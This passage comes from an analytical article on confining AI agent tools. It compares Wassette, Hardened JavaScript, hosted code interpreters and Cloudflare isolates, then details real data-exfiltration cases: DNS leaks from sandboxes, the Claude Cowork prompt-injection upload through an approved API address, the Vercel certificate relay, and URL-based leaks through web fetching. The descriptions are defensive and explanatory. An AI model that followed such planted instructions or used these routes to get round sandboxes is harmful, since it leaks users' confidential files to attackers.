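Users must also trust Wasmtime. It is an ordinary process with the user's permissions, so code that breaks out of its sandbox has the same access as any local server. The most dangerous flaws in a WebAssembly runtime are compilation errors. Wasmtime translates each component into the processor's own instructions and has to make sure that every memory access stays inside the component's block. A mistake may let a component read or change the runtime's memory.

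Version 0.3.4 of Wassette, from November 2025, fixed two published vulnerabilities in software it depends on. One was in the Wasmtime code that connects the host program to a component, the boundary Wassette relies on for security. The other was in a library that unpacks archives, and it could let a crafted archive smuggle in extra files. An earlier release that autumn had switched off an automatic security audit "to reduce CI noise", or unwanted alerts from the project's build system. That was an odd choice for a project that describes itself as security-oriented, though the later fixes show that the maintainers still act on published flaws.

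Wassette 0.4.0 uses Wasmtime 38.0.4, so its users don't get fixes from later Wasmtime versions unless they rebuild Wassette with a newer one. Containers also depend on kernel fixes, but operating-system vendors deliver those automatically to most users, whereas a small project like Wassette has to publish a new release each time. Microsoft has documented how to run Wassette inside a Docker container, which would give an attacker a second barrier to break.

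### Is anyone using it?

Wassette 0.4.0 came out on 4 February 2026 and was still the latest release in June, according to GitPedia's *Wassette*. That page also reproduces the project's introduction, which warns that Wassette is "not production ready yet" and may change significantly. Microsoft's FAQ says the company uses Wassette and is actively developing it, but gives no examples of what it uses it for.

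Outside interest is modest. In late January 2026 the project had 817 stars and 56 copies made by other developers, according to Ecosyste.ms, a service that tracks open-source software. The team behind the MoonBit programming language published a tutorial on building a weather tool for Wassette. This attention isn't evidence that people rely on the project. Many of the available components are Microsoft's own examples, such as a clock, a calculator and a search tool for scientific papers.

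Other projects also use WebAssembly to confine tools. Hyper-MCP, for example, runs each plugin in its own WebAssembly virtual machine, with no access to files or the network by default, according to the security wiki OffSecML. Microsoft objects that most earlier WebAssembly platforms require their own libraries, so a tool written for one won't run on another. Standard components should avoid this problem, and a developer could use a component written for Wassette elsewhere if Microsoft abandoned the project.

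### Hardened JavaScript

Hardened JavaScript, like WebAssembly, can run a plugin that starts with no access to outside resources. It is a restricted form of JavaScript that lets one program run code from people who don't trust each other. The host program first freezes the language's built-in objects, so that one plugin can't tamper with a function that another uses. It then runs each plugin in a compartment, which has the basic features of the language but no access to the network, files or clock. The plugin can use only the objects that the host passes to it, and each of these works as a capability. MetaMask, a cryptocurrency wallet, uses this method to run third-party extensions called Snaps.

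The host can make these capabilities very narrow. Wassette grants the weather tool access to a network address, and the component decides what to send there. A hardened JavaScript host could instead give the plugin a single function, `getForecast(city)`, written by the host's developer. The function would look up the city in a fixed list, build the request and return the forecast. A plugin with only this function could not add a clause of the contract to a request, but it could still leak a little through its choice of city. With 1,024 cities on the list, each call could send ten bits to the forecasting service.

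WebAssembly components could work the same way, because their interfaces can import any function the host implements. Wassette's policies cover only storage, network hosts, environment variables and memory, so users who want narrower permissions would have to add them to Wassette's code. These would be useful for tools that contact one service for one purpose. For example, the host could give an email tool a function that sends only to recipients the user has named.

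Compartments give weaker isolation than components in other respects. They normally share one process with the host, so a flaw in the JavaScript engine exposes everything in that process, and a plugin stuck in an endless loop can freeze the host. For reasons like these, MetaMask also runs each Snap in its own isolated environment. The host's developer also has to be careful about which objects to pass to a compartment, because passing an object also grants access to any more powerful object that can be reached through it.

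Most existing MCP servers would need changes to run in Hardened JavaScript, even though it looks easier to adopt than WebAssembly because JavaScript is one of the two most popular languages for these servers. They load Node.js's file and network modules directly, which a compartment doesn't provide. Either the developer has to rewrite the server to accept narrower functions from the host, or the host has to supply its own versions of those modules and check each use.

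## Code execution without a network connection

A code interpreter is a tool that runs the programs a model writes. If a user uploads a spreadsheet and asks for the average of a column, the model writes a few lines of Python, the interpreter runs them, and the model reads the result. The interpreter needs only the input, a processor and somewhere to write the answer. It is the easiest tool to confine because it can do most of its work without a network connection.

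An interpreter can also replace some third-party tools. The lawyer's agent could write its own script to turn the contract into a PDF, so the lawyer wouldn't need the stranger's converter.

Outsiders can still influence code that runs without a network connection. The model writes the code just before it runs, usually nobody reads it, and text in an uploaded file can change what the model writes through prompt injection. The code also imports libraries that other people wrote. A confined interpreter therefore has to be safe even if the program inside it is written to steal the data.

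The four questions have unusually good answers for a well-built interpreter:

1. Who starts it? Usually the company that runs the model, or a cloud provider that the application's developer chose. If the model's own provider runs the interpreter, the data reaches no new company.
2. Which authority does it begin with? It can have a processor, some libraries, the user's files and scratch storage, with no network and no way to call other tools.
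3. Who can verify that? The user mostly has to rely on the provider's documentation, although anyone can run test programs inside the interpreter.
4. What does its reply reach? It reaches the model, and through the model any other tool the agent has.

### Two hosted interpreters

Anthropic runs an interpreter on its own servers for developers who build on Claude. According to Anthropic's *Code execution tool*, the code runs in a Linux container with one processor, 5 GiB of memory, 5 GiB of disk space and no internet access. Each request to the model gets a new container unless the developer's application sends back the ID of an earlier one. Claude can't install packages, so it can use only the libraries already in the container.

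Those libraries are probably enough for the lawyer. They include python-docx, which reads word-processor files, and reportlab, which writes PDFs. A script that used both might lose some of the contract's formatting, but a malicious instruction in the contract could not make the script upload the contract anywhere.

Amazon Web Services (AWS) offers AgentCore Code Interpreter to developers who build agents on its platform. Each interpreter runs in a microVM. The developer must choose one of three network modes when creating an interpreter, because the network setting is a required field in AWS's *CodeInterpreterNetworkConfiguration*. Sandbox mode gives the code access to Amazon's S3 file storage, and Public mode gives it internet access. VPC mode connects it to the customer's own private network within AWS, where the customer sets the network rules.

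| | Anthropic's code execution tool | AgentCore in sandbox mode |
|---|---|---|
| Isolation | Container | MicroVM |
| Lifetime | One request by default, up to 30 days if reused | 15 minutes by default, up to 8 hours |
| Network | None | S3 only |
| Libraries | Pre-installed only | More than 270 pre-installed |

Sandbox mode is not confinement in Lampson's sense, because it allows access to S3, where attackers can rent storage too. The Wassette policy entry that allowed every S3 address had the same problem. A customer would need to know whether AWS restricts the interpreter to the customer's own storage.

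The interpreter may also have access to more of the customer's data than it needs. It reads from AWS services through a role, which is a set of permissions the customer assigns. BeyondTrust, a security company, found that the default role in AWS's starter kit could read every S3 file in the account and every stored password and key.

### Why developers open the network

The most common reason to want a connection is to download packages. Python and JavaScript programmers often use libraries from public registries, and an interpreter that can't download them can use only what its operator installed. The documentation for Serverless, a framework for deploying cloud software, lists calling online services and downloading packages as the uses for AgentCore's public mode.

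Large files are another reason to allow S3 access from a sandbox. AgentCore accepts files of up to 100 MB inside a request and up to 5 GB through S3, according to AWS's *Execute code and analyze data using Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter*. BeyondTrust describes S3 access from sandbox mode as a key customer requirement when AWS built the product.

Software development needs both packages and access to a code repository. InfoQ (2025) reported that Claude Code on the web, a separate Anthropic product, copies the user's repository to a virtual machine and sets its internet access according to the user's settings. The machine has a narrow route to GitHub through an outside proxy and never holds the user's GitHub token. The proxy checks each operation, for example that the code is going to the agreed branch, and then adds the token. A similar check on outgoing email would have caught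 postmark-mcp's hidden recipient.

Allowing network access only to a package registry such as npm can still let data out, because anyone with an account can publish there. Malicious code could include the attacker's login details and use them to publish a user's file, such as a contract, as a package.

An operator can supply packages without opening the network by installing popular libraries in advance, as Anthropic and AWS do, or by having a trusted program fetch the packages before the sandbox starts and pass them in along with the code. With either method, a compromised library can still run inside the sandbox, but it cannot use the network to send out what it reads.

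Anthropic's interpreter still has no network connection, but the code it runs may now be able to act outside the container through other tools. The August 2025 version runs commands and handles files. The January 2026 version also lets the code call the other tools in the developer's request. If one of them sends email, the code can send email, even though the container itself can't contact any address. This can still be safe, because the developer decides which tools to include and can check each call to their own tools. But the lack of internet access is no longer enough to show that the code can't affect anything outside the container.

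### Sandboxes that still answered name lookups

In 2026, researchers showed that two interpreters that their operators had advertised as cut off from the internet could leak data through name lookups. Before a program contacts a website, it looks up the numerical address for the site's name in the Domain Name System (DNS). If the nearest DNS server doesn't have the address, it forwards the query, which eventually reaches a server run by the name's owner. The name can contain data, so the owner may receive that data even if the program never connects to the site.

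Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) reported that a single malicious prompt could make a conversation leak the user's messages and uploaded files through the environment where ChatGPT runs code. OpenAI's help pages had said that this environment could not make direct outbound requests, according to VPNCentral's *ChatGPT flaw allowed silent data exfiltration*. The prompt could come from a user who had copied it from somewhere, or from a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that another person has set up. In the second case, the attacker is in much the same position as the developer of a malicious tool server.

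OpenAI fixed the flaw on 20 February 2026, before Check Point published its findings. According to Security Point Break's *ChatGPT Issue Could Have Enabled Silent Data Leakage* (2026), OpenAI told the researchers that it had already found the problem itself. The Hacker News (2026) reported that there was no evidence of malicious use.

AWS took much longer to close the same kind of channel. BeyondTrust's researchers reported the flaw on 1 September 2025, according to the company's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter’s ‘Sandbox’ mode allows DNS queries* (2026). AWS reproduced it within days and deployed a fix on 1 November, then withdrew the fix. In December it told the researchers it would change the documentation instead. It rated the flaw's severity 7.5 out of 10 and sent the researcher who reported it a $100 gift card.

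BeyondTrust published its findings on 16 March 2026. AWS responded that its services were operating as expected and that sandbox mode needed name lookups to reach S3, but it closed the channel in mid-April. BeyondTrust now says data can no longer leave this way.

AWS's first position was partly reasonable, because a sandbox that has to find S3 by name needs some form of DNS lookup. But it needs to look up only a few names, and this sandbox could look up any name on the internet. AWS had also originally advertised the mode as offering "complete isolation with no external access", so customers had no reason to suspect a channel to the outside.

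The researchers used a service that the sandbox provided, without breaking out of the microVM, so stronger isolation would not have helped.

The case also shows that the third question is hard to answer by testing. When the BeyondTrust researchers first tried to contact an outside server from inside the sandbox, the command appeared to fail. They could see that the lookup had arrived only in their own server's log. A customer who ran the same test and checked only the result inside the sandbox would have concluded that the sandbox was closed.

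AWS's automatic compliance rule *bedrockagentcore-codeinterpreter-networkmode-check* flags any custom interpreter in public or sandbox mode, so only VPC mode passes. But Gębala (2026), in *AWS Bedrock AgentCore*, reported that on 26 April VPC mode still answered outside DNS lookups unless the customer had added a DNS filter. This is one practitioner's test, and he promotes his own auditing tool, but the result fits AWS's description of VPC mode as giving customers control over lookups. An administrator who switched to VPC mode to satisfy the rule and changed nothing else could have made the interpreter leakier.

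A tool that the user confines on their own computer also can't send a DNS lookup if it has no network connection. If the user filters the connection instead of removing it, the filter has to cover DNS lookups as well as web requests.

### Cloudflare's isolates

Some of the most useful programs an agent could write need other tools. For example, a script might search the lawyer's calendar and document store, then post a summary to colleagues. Cloudflare, which runs other people's websites and programs on its servers, has a design that lets a script do this without a network connection.

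Varda and Pai (2025) argued in *Code Mode* that the usual way of calling tools is inefficient because every reply passes through the model, even if the model only copies it into the next call. They proposed turning each MCP server's tools into functions in TypeScript, a form of JavaScript, and having the model write one program that calls them. They expected models to handle more tools, and more complicated ones, this way because models have seen far more real code than tool calls. Cloudflare later reported that the conversion could cut the text the model has to process by 81%.

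Suppose the lawyer asks which contracts in the document store expire this month, and wants the list posted in the deal team's chat room. On Cloudflare's system it could go like this:

1. The parent program, which plays the part of the client application, collects the tool descriptions from the document server and the chat server and turns them into TypeScript definitions.
2. The model reads the definitions and writes a program that fetches the contracts, compares the dates and posts the list.
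3. The parent starts a new isolate, a separate instance of the JavaScript engine that Google Chrome uses, and loads the program into it. The isolate has no network connection. It receives one object for the document server and one for the chat server.
4. When the program calls a function on either object, the call goes back to the parent. The parent adds the access token and forwards the request to the server.
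5. The program prints a short confirmation, which the parent returns to the model, and the parent discards the isolate.

The program never receives a token, so it can't leak one. It also can't contact any server for which it has no object. Normally, the contracts would pass through the model before the comparison. Here they stay in the isolate, so a malicious instruction in one of them reaches the model only if the program prints it.

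#### A factory with chosen outward channels

This design resembles the KeyKOS factory. Cloudflare's *Bindings* describes the company's objects as capabilities, which a program can have only if it receives them. In a mailing list post, *Sandboxing in Cloudflare Workers*, Varda (2025) called the design a capability-based permissions model.

| KeyKOS factory | Cloudflare's system |
|---|---|
| The developer seals a program in the factory | The parent supplies the program's code |
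| The developer lists the capabilities that every copy gets | The parent lists the objects and sets the network option |
| The customer gets a fresh copy | The parent can start a new isolate for each run |
| The customer asks the factory whether copies have outward authority | The parent's developer reads the settings, because nothing answers the customer |

When the parent blocks the network, the isolate's only outward channels are the objects that the parent's developer chose to pass in. Passing in none suits a document converter.

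The main difference is in the last row of the table. On Cloudflare, the application's developer controls the settings, and the lawyer has to trust that the developer got them right.

These settings are easy to get wrong. According to Cloudflare's *Dynamic Workers*, a developer blocks the network by setting `globalOutbound` to `null`. If the developer leaves the option out, the isolate inherits the parent's access, which usually means the whole internet. Some of Cloudflare's own sample code, including a sample for programs that use npm packages, leaves it out. A developer who copied that sample to run a stranger's converter would give the converter an open connection. AWS's required field is better in this respect because it forces the developer to choose.

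The parent can also leak data by accident through logs. The same documentation shows how to collect whatever the program prints and send it to an outside address for monitoring. If the program prints a paragraph of the contract, that paragraph goes there too. A list of the ways data can leave an isolate should therefore include its logs.

#### How narrow an object can be

Cloudflare's *Egress control* recommends blocking the isolate's internet access and then granting it specific objects as the most secure design. Cloudflare also supports a gateway that intercepts every web request from the isolate and can refuse or change it. The gateway suits programs that rely on existing web libraries.

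Varda, Pai and Gupta argue in *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* that filtering requests is harder than writing a small object that offers only the permitted operations. A gateway has to understand every request well enough to decide whether it is safe, and a request can carry meaning in its address, headers and body. Their argument applies to the recipient check that postmark-mcp would have needed.

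Cloudflare's chat-room example uses a narrow object with a single function, `post`, which takes text. The parent fixes the room, the access token and the sender's name, so the program can't post anywhere else or pose as someone else. But the text can be anything, including a whole contract, and everyone in the room can read it. To keep the program from posting a contract, the parent would have to check the text or replace the free text with a more limited input, such as a list of contract numbers and dates.

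The isolate also confines only the program the model wrote. The MCP servers behind the objects run elsewhere with whatever authority they had before. If the chat server copied every message to its developer, as postmark-mcp did with email, the isolate would not stop it. Lampson's point about confined programs that call unconfined ones applies here.

A parent can also use an isolate to confine a third-party tool, if the tool is written in JavaScript or Python or compiled to WebAssembly. Cloudflare's bundling library downloads any npm packages the tool needs before the isolate starts. The download happens outside the sandbox, but the library only combines the packages as text, so no third-party code runs until the limits are in place. AgentBound's installation step lacked this protection.

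#### Are isolates strong enough?

Isolates are lighter than containers but easier to break out of. Varda and colleagues acknowledge that security flaws are more common in V8, the JavaScript engine, than in typical hypervisors. A program that exploited such a flaw might reach the parent or another customer's data, since new isolates usually run on the same machine as the parent and often in the same thread. Cloudflare says it installs V8 security fixes within hours, surrounds the isolates with a second sandbox and watches for malicious code. Cloudflare sells the service, so its account is not independent evidence, but it has run customers' code in isolates for eight years.

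An isolate starts in a few milliseconds, so the parent can create a new one for every run and discard it afterward. Varda and colleagues point out that developers who use slower containers may be tempted to reuse them for several tasks, which weakens security.

Cloudflare's prices also give developers a reason to reuse isolates, though a weaker one. After the first 1,000 each month, every new isolate costs $0.002, so 100,000 single-use runs in a month would cost about $200, plus processor time. A developer can avoid most of that by giving the code a fixed ID, which lets Cloudflare reuse an isolate that is already running. For a tool that handles different customers' contracts, the saving doesn't justify the reuse.

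### Storage that outlasts a run

A program with no network can still pass data to a later run, if the two share storage.

| Service | What can outlast a run | How long it lasts |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's code execution tool | Files in a container that the application reuses | Up to 30 days |
| Anthropic's code execution tool | Finished files that Claude hands back | Until someone deletes them |
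| AgentCore | Files in the same session | Up to 8 hours |
| Cloudflare | Memory in a reused isolate | No fixed period |
| Cloudflare | Files in an optional workspace | Across runs, by design |

AWS's *Session management* describes the simplest of these rules, which is that data disappears when the session ends. Anthropic's tool is nearly as simple if the application never reuses a container. If an application kept one container for all of a law firm's clients, a script working on one client's contract could read the other clients' contracts. Anthropic limits containers to the developer's workspace, a division of the account, but this doesn't separate clients whose work shares a workspace.

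Cloudflare's reused isolates are harder to reason about because two requests with the same ID may reach the same isolate or different ones. A developer can't assume that memory will persist between requests or that it will be cleared.

Storage that an application deliberately provides needs the most care. In Cloudflare's example of a shared database, the parent adds the customer's number to the name of every record, so that each program can read only that customer's records. This protection depends on a few lines of the parent's code, and it doesn't prevent problems within one customer's own storage. A program influenced by a malicious spreadsheet could leave text in the workspace for a later program to act on, much like an injection saved in an agent's notes.

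An interpreter's operator also keeps some data. Anthropic retains the contents of its code execution containers for up to 30 days, and the tool isn't eligible for the company's zero-retention arrangement. This doesn't break confinement, but a lawyer who has promised a client that nobody will store a contract can't use the tool on that contract.

### The answer that goes back to the model

The interpreter's output to the model is the one channel that can't be closed without making the tool useless. This output can contain text planted in the file, which has the same effect as the planted issue in the GitHub attack.

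Code Mode makes this channel smaller because the program can select what to return. In one of Cloudflare's examples, a program reads up to 1,000 chat messages and returns only those from one colleague, so the model never sees the rest. The parent could also accept only certain kinds of answer. If the lawyer asks for a total, the parent can reject anything but a number. A number can't contain an instruction to send an email, though its digits could still encode a little of the contract.

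Many questions need an answer in words, though, and then the risk depends on the agent's other tools. Anthropic's current web search and web fetch tools automatically start the code interpreter to filter pages before the model reads them. An agent that uses these tools can therefore work on private files in the code interpreter, which has no network connection, and contact the web in the same request, and the model can pass data between them.

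## Claude Cowork: data that left through an approved address

An agent that does office work usually needs some network access, if only to reach the company that runs its model. Developers often limit this access with an address allowlist, which names the addresses that code in the sandbox may contact and blocks the rest. Anthropic used one in Claude Cowork, which it released as a research preview in January 2026. Two days later, PromptArmor published a demonstration in which Cowork sent a user's files to a stranger through one of the approved addresses.

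### A loan estimate in a stranger's account

The victim in PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* has a folder of confidential property documents. The attack goes like this:

1. The user connects Cowork to the folder and uploads a Word document from the internet. The document looks like a skill, a file of instructions that shows Claude how to do some kind of task. It also contains further instructions in text too small and pale to see.
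2. The user asks Cowork to analyse the folder with the help of the skill, and Claude reads the hidden instructions along with the visible ones.
3. The hidden instructions tell Claude to upload the largest file it can find to Anthropic's own file storage service. They include an API key, a secret string that tells a service which account a program is acting for. This key belongs to the attacker.
4. The file, a loan estimate with financial figures and partial Social Security numbers, arrives in the attacker's Anthropic account. The attacker can then ask Claude questions about it.

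Cowork never asked the user to approve the upload. The demonstration used Claude Haiku, a small model. In a second test, Opus 4.5, which resists injections better, uploaded customer records after a user gave it a malicious integration guide. These were single demonstrations, so they show that the attack could work but not how often.

Anthropic already knew about the weakness. The security researcher Johann Rehberger had described it in October 2025, in Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*, after Claude's code interpreter gained network access. SecurityWeek's *Claude AI APIs Can Be Abused for Data Exfiltration* noted that this access was on by default on certain plans. The default setting was called "Package managers only", but it also approved Anthropic's API address, as Underhill (2025) pointed out in *Hackers Turn Claude AI Into Data Thief With New Attack*.

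After Rehberger's report, Anthropic said it would treat such leaks as reportable flaws and urged users to monitor Claude's network access or turn it off, according to TechRadar's *Claude can be tricked into sending your private company data to hackers*. But it had not fixed the underlying problem when it released Cowork, whose users are less likely to be programmers. Anthropic advised them to look out for "suspicious actions that may indicate prompt injection". Willison thought this was unfair to ask of people who don't write code. *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* (Apostol, 2026) reported that by 16 January Anthropic had acknowledged the risk and was updating Cowork's virtual machine.

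### Every part of the sandbox worked

Anthropic published its own account of the leak in May 2026. Its summary was "The sandbox worked perfectly, and yet the data was exfiltrated."

| Part of the sandbox | Its job | What happened in the attack |
|---|---|---|
| Virtual machine | Keep Claude's code away from the rest of the computer | The code stayed inside |
| Folder access | Expose only the folders the user selected | The stolen file was in a selected folder |
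| Credential storage outside the virtual machine | Keep the user's keys away from the code | The attacker supplied a different key |
| Address filter | Block connections to unapproved addresses | The upload went to an approved address |

The third row is the least obvious because sandbox designers worry a lot about code that steals the user's credentials, and this theft did not need them. Cowork kept those credentials in the computer's keychain, where the code could not read them, but the attacker wanted the file to end up in the attacker's own account. That required getting a credential for that account into the sandbox, and any document that Claude reads can carry one.

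The address filter had to allow `api.anthropic.com` because Cowork's agent called its model there. But that address also handles file storage for every Anthropic customer. Allowing it therefore also allowed file uploads to any Anthropic account, and anyone could open one.

Anthropic concluded that an allowlist is better understood as a capability grant than as a list of safe destinations, because an attacker can use every function behind an approved address. This grant is much coarser than a KeyKOS capability. In KeyKOS, a program that held a capability for the user's own file store could not use it to write to someone else's. An allowlist only lets the sandbox reach an address, and the key in each request determines what that request is allowed to do there, so whoever controls the request can choose the key.

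A malicious tool could do this without prompt injection. Suppose the lawyer's converter runs in a container that can contact only the model provider, which the lawyer already trusts with the contracts. The lawyer approved that address because the developer says the converter uses a model to tidy up the layout. The developer could put a key for their own account in the code, and the converter could use it to upload each contract to that account.

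### The repair

Anthropic added a proxy inside the virtual machine that intercepts traffic to its API. If a script tries to upload the contract, this now happens:

1. The script sends its request to `api.anthropic.com`, and the proxy intercepts it.
2. The proxy checks the credential. Cowork gives each virtual machine a session token with fewer permissions than the user's own login, and the proxy rejects a request that carries any other key.
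3. The proxy looks for headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something from the web, and blocks the request if it finds any.
4. If the request passes both checks, the proxy sends it on.

The third step matters because a service that fetches pages for its callers can send data to addresses that the sandbox blocks. A script could put a clause of the contract into the URL of a page on the attacker's server and have Anthropic's machines request that page. The sandbox's filter would detect only a connection to Anthropic.

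Anthropic put the proxy in the virtual machine because its servers can't distinguish Cowork's requests from those of any other customer's program. The attacker's key was valid, so the servers accepted it. The check therefore has to happen on the user's side, but it could run on the user's computer outside the virtual machine, which might be safer. Anthropic enforces two of Cowork's six main isolation mechanisms outside the virtual machine's kernel, so they would keep working if an attacker took complete control inside the machine. A proxy there presumably lacks that protection.

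Some designs allow a simpler fix. Anthropic moved Cowork's agent loop, the part that calls the model, out of the virtual machine and left only code execution inside. If the scripts running there never need to call the model, the model's address could be removed from their list of approved addresses.

The repair closes the route to other people's Anthropic accounts. A malicious script may still be able to upload files to the user's own account, if the session token permits it, but the attacker would then need a way into that account. Binding a channel to an account does not help once someone has stolen the account's credentials. Help Net Security's *Stolen Claude API keys can turn Claude Code into a remote-controlled implant* (2026) notes that a standard API key gives access to more of Anthropic's platform than the OAuth credentials from a login, and that OpenAI's API has an equivalent upload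 function.

The fix also covers only traffic from the virtual machine. A stranger's converter installed as a local plugin runs outside the virtual machine, so the fix does not affect it.

Outsiders know these details because Anthropic chose to publish them. Willison (2026) praised the account and said he often has trouble deciding how far to trust a sandbox because makers rarely document their sandboxes thoroughly. Good documentation helps users choose a product, but it doesn't let them check that the copy they are running matches it.

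### Code hosts and package registries

The same attack could work through any other approved address where strangers can open accounts. The two most common kinds are probably code hosts such as GitHub and package registries such as npm.

Developers approve registries so that agents can download libraries, but malicious code can also use an approved registry to publish the user's files, as it could in a code interpreter. OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, can't download libraries by default because it starts commands with no network access, according to OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox*.

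Access to package registries is fairly easy to restrict. Installing public packages requires only downloads, so a proxy that reads requests can allow downloads and refuse publishing. An operator can also cut off the sandbox's access before it receives any private data. Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* (2026) includes sample code that permits a few hosts, installs a project's packages and then blocks all web requests without restarting the sandbox. This is safe only if the user's files arrive after the block is in place. Otherwise it has the same gap as AgentBound's installation step.

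Code hosts are harder, because agents need to write to them as well as read. Claude Code on the web handles this with the proxy that checks the branch before it adds the user's GitHub token. The program inside the sandbox logs in to that proxy with a credential made only for this purpose, which the proxy also verifies. An attacker's GitHub key won't work there, because the program has no direct connection to GitHub.

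A proxy can add the right credential to a request and still let the wrong one through. Cloudflare's sample for GitHub attaches a secret token to each request outside the sandbox, so the code never sees it. But the sample sets one header and forwards the others unchanged. If malicious code put the attacker's credential in a different header, the service would receive both and have to choose which to accept. A careful developer would have the proxy delete any credential it did not add.

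Sometimes the list doesn't apply. GitLab runs the agents on its development platform in a sandbox that always permits GitLab's own address and a few others. If the sandbox can't start, the agent's job runs without one, and the only sign is a warning in the log. Administrators can now make such jobs fail instead, but projects that use their own container images can still get around this setting.

### The Vercel flaw: an approved server as courier

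In October 2026 researchers described a leak that account checks might not have caught. Vercel, a web hosting company, sells a sandbox in which developers run code written by agents. According to *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox* (Tuttle, 2026), each sandbox is a microVM, and a firewall outside it controls the network. When a program opens an encrypted connection, the firewall reads the host name, which the program sends unencrypted at the start, and checks it against the user's list of allowed hosts. It checks name lookups against the same list. If the host is on the list, the firewall normally passes the rest of the connection through without decrypting it.

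AIR, a security startup, found a way past this filter without the sandbox contacting an unapproved address. Smalley (2026) explains in *Sandbox vulnerability gives rogue AI agents a path to escape* that the researchers designed a digital certificate for a program in the sandbox to send to an approved server. When the approved server processed the certificate, it sent a request containing the data to a server that the attacker controlled.

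The firewall correctly identified the destination of every connection it saw. In the Cowork leak, the data stayed at the approved service but in the wrong account. In the Vercel leak, an approved server passed the data on to a machine that was not on the list. The Vercel leak is closer to the page-fetching problem in step 3 of Anthropic's repair, except that the fetching was a side effect of checking a certificate, not a feature the service offered.

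Vercel did not immediately answer the reporter's request for comment, so its response is known only through AIR. Niv Hoffman, AIR's co-founder, said Vercel had asked for time because it was not yet clear how to fix the flaw. He said AIR had no evidence that anyone had used the flaw in an attack but could not rule it out, since the flaw seemed to have existed for a long time. AIR has a commercial interest in alarming customers about sandboxes, but Vercel had also warned about this class of problem two months earlier, when Tuttle listed "a trusted package service turned into a relay" among the ways network limits fail.

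A check on the account would have come too late, because programs exchange certificates before they send the request that names an account. Vercel has a stricter mode that might help. For addresses where the user wants to add credentials or inspect requests, the firewall decrypts the program's connection and opens a new one to the service, so a certificate from the sandbox should get no further than the firewall. Using this mode for every address would let the firewall read all the sandbox's traffic, and it would break programs that accept only the service's own certificate.

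### Narrowing a channel to an account and an operation

An approved address is safe for private data only if the sandbox also controls which account each request uses and what the request does. Cowork's first version controlled neither. The GitHub attack and the hidden recipient in postmark-mcp both leaked data through the user's own account, so controlling the account alone isn't enough.

Some common services make this narrowing much easier than others:

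| Service | How to limit the account | How to limit the operation |
|---|---|---|
| Language-model API | Accept only the session's own token | Permit model calls, and refuse file uploads and page fetching |
| File storage such as Amazon S3 | Approve the address of one storage bucket | Permit reading or writing, whichever the task needs |
| Code host | Have a proxy hold a token for one repository | Check the branch, and refuse new public pages |
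| Package registry | Public downloads need no account | Refuse publishing, or remove access after installation |
| Email provider | Have a trusted layer hold the token | Check the recipients and the text |

S3 is the easiest to limit by account. Each bucket can have its own host name, so even a filter that reads only host names can allow only one bucket, as Vercel's documentation suggests. This doesn't help if the user approves all of S3 with a wildcard, or if outsiders can read the approved bucket. A company that runs its own GitLab server gets a similar benefit, because strangers probably can't open accounts there.

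Model APIs and most other web services put all their customers behind one host name and distinguish them by key. A proxy usually can't determine whose key a request carries, so it has to issue or hold the correct one and reject all others. It also has to decrypt the traffic. Cloudflare and Vercel do this with a certificate authority created for each sandbox, which the programs inside trust by default. Vercel's firewall can then match requests by path, method, query or header, so a user could let a script submit results to a service but not read anything there. For rules that depend on the contents of the request, the firewall can forward traffic to a proxy that the customer writes.

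Writing such rules requires knowing what each service does, and services add functions. An address that offered only model calls when a developer approved it may offer file storage a year later. A rule that lists permitted operations will block the new function by default, but a rule that lists forbidden ones will let it through.

Each of these checks also adds new code in a sensitive place. The address filter that failed in Cowork was custom software, and the repair added a custom proxy. PCQuest's *AI API keys at risk* describes a flaw in the proxy used by Docker Sandboxes, which runs coding agents in microVMs. The proxy sits outside the microVMs, holds the user's API keys and adds them to requests. A researcher at Endor Labs found that a change to a third-party agent kit, a package of settings for an agent, could make the proxy send keys to destinations the developer had never approved.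 The flaw affected 13 services, including OpenAI, Anthropic and GitHub. Docker fixed it on 30 November 2026 by making the proxy enforce the approved destinations for each key.

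## Web search and page fetching: when the request itself carries data

Anthropic's proxy for Cowork can be strict because a script there needs only one account and a few operations. A research agent, however, needs to open pages that nobody listed in advance, on sites that strangers run. To read a page, the agent has to send a request, and whoever receives the request can read it. Search and page fetching can therefore send data out, even though people often call them read-only and they rarely change anything on the web.

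### Who receives a search and who receives a fetch

Suppose the lawyer asks an agent whether the purchase in the contract needs a competition authority's approval. The agent might search for both companies' names and the word "merger". The search provider would then learn of a deal that neither company has announced. The owner of a page in the results would learn nothing unless the agent opened that page, and would then see which address the agent requested and when.

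The search provider sees every query, but it is a single company that the user can identify. If the model's developer runs the search, the query may reach nobody who hasn't already seen the conversation. Queries are therefore mainly a privacy problem. A page owner sees only requests for its own pages, but an attacker can own one, so fetches are an easier way to steal data. A search tool from an unknown developer carries both risks, since the developer may see every query.

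An address can also contain a lot of information about the user. OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links* gives the harmless example of a car-search link that includes the user's city, so opening it reveals to the site that the user lives in London. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* warns that website publishers may keep any parameters in the addresses that Claude requests.

*Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) describes a working attack of this kind. The researchers hid instructions in a blog post and had an agent summarise it. The agent looked up a confidential project in the company's knowledge base, put the details in a URL on the attacker's server, and requested it. The web tool alone supplied two parts of the lethal trifecta, because it both brought in the instructions and sent out the data.

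Some requests meant to read a page also store data on the server. Willison describes a flaw in Superhuman's email assistant, which allowed images from `docs.google.com`. That host also serves Google Forms, which saves data sent in an ordinary page request. A planted email got the assistant to submit the contents of dozens of messages to an attacker's form.

### Anthropic's rule: the address must already be in the conversation

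Anthropic does not let its fetch tool open an address that Claude has composed. This blocks the attack in the blog-post experiment, whatever the model has been persuaded to do. The details differ between products:

| Where the address appeared | Claude API, June 2026 | Claude Managed Agents, since 7 October 2026 | Claude chat app, since July 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user's message | Yes | Yes | Yes |
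| A search result | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| A page the tool fetched earlier | Yes | Yes | No |
| A reply from a tool that the client application runs | Yes | No | Unclear |
| Claude's own text | No | No | No |

The first column comes from Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* and the second from its *Claude Platform release notes* (2026). Managed Agents is Anthropic's service for running agents on its own servers. The third column follows Willison's account of a flaw that Ayush Paul found in the chat app.

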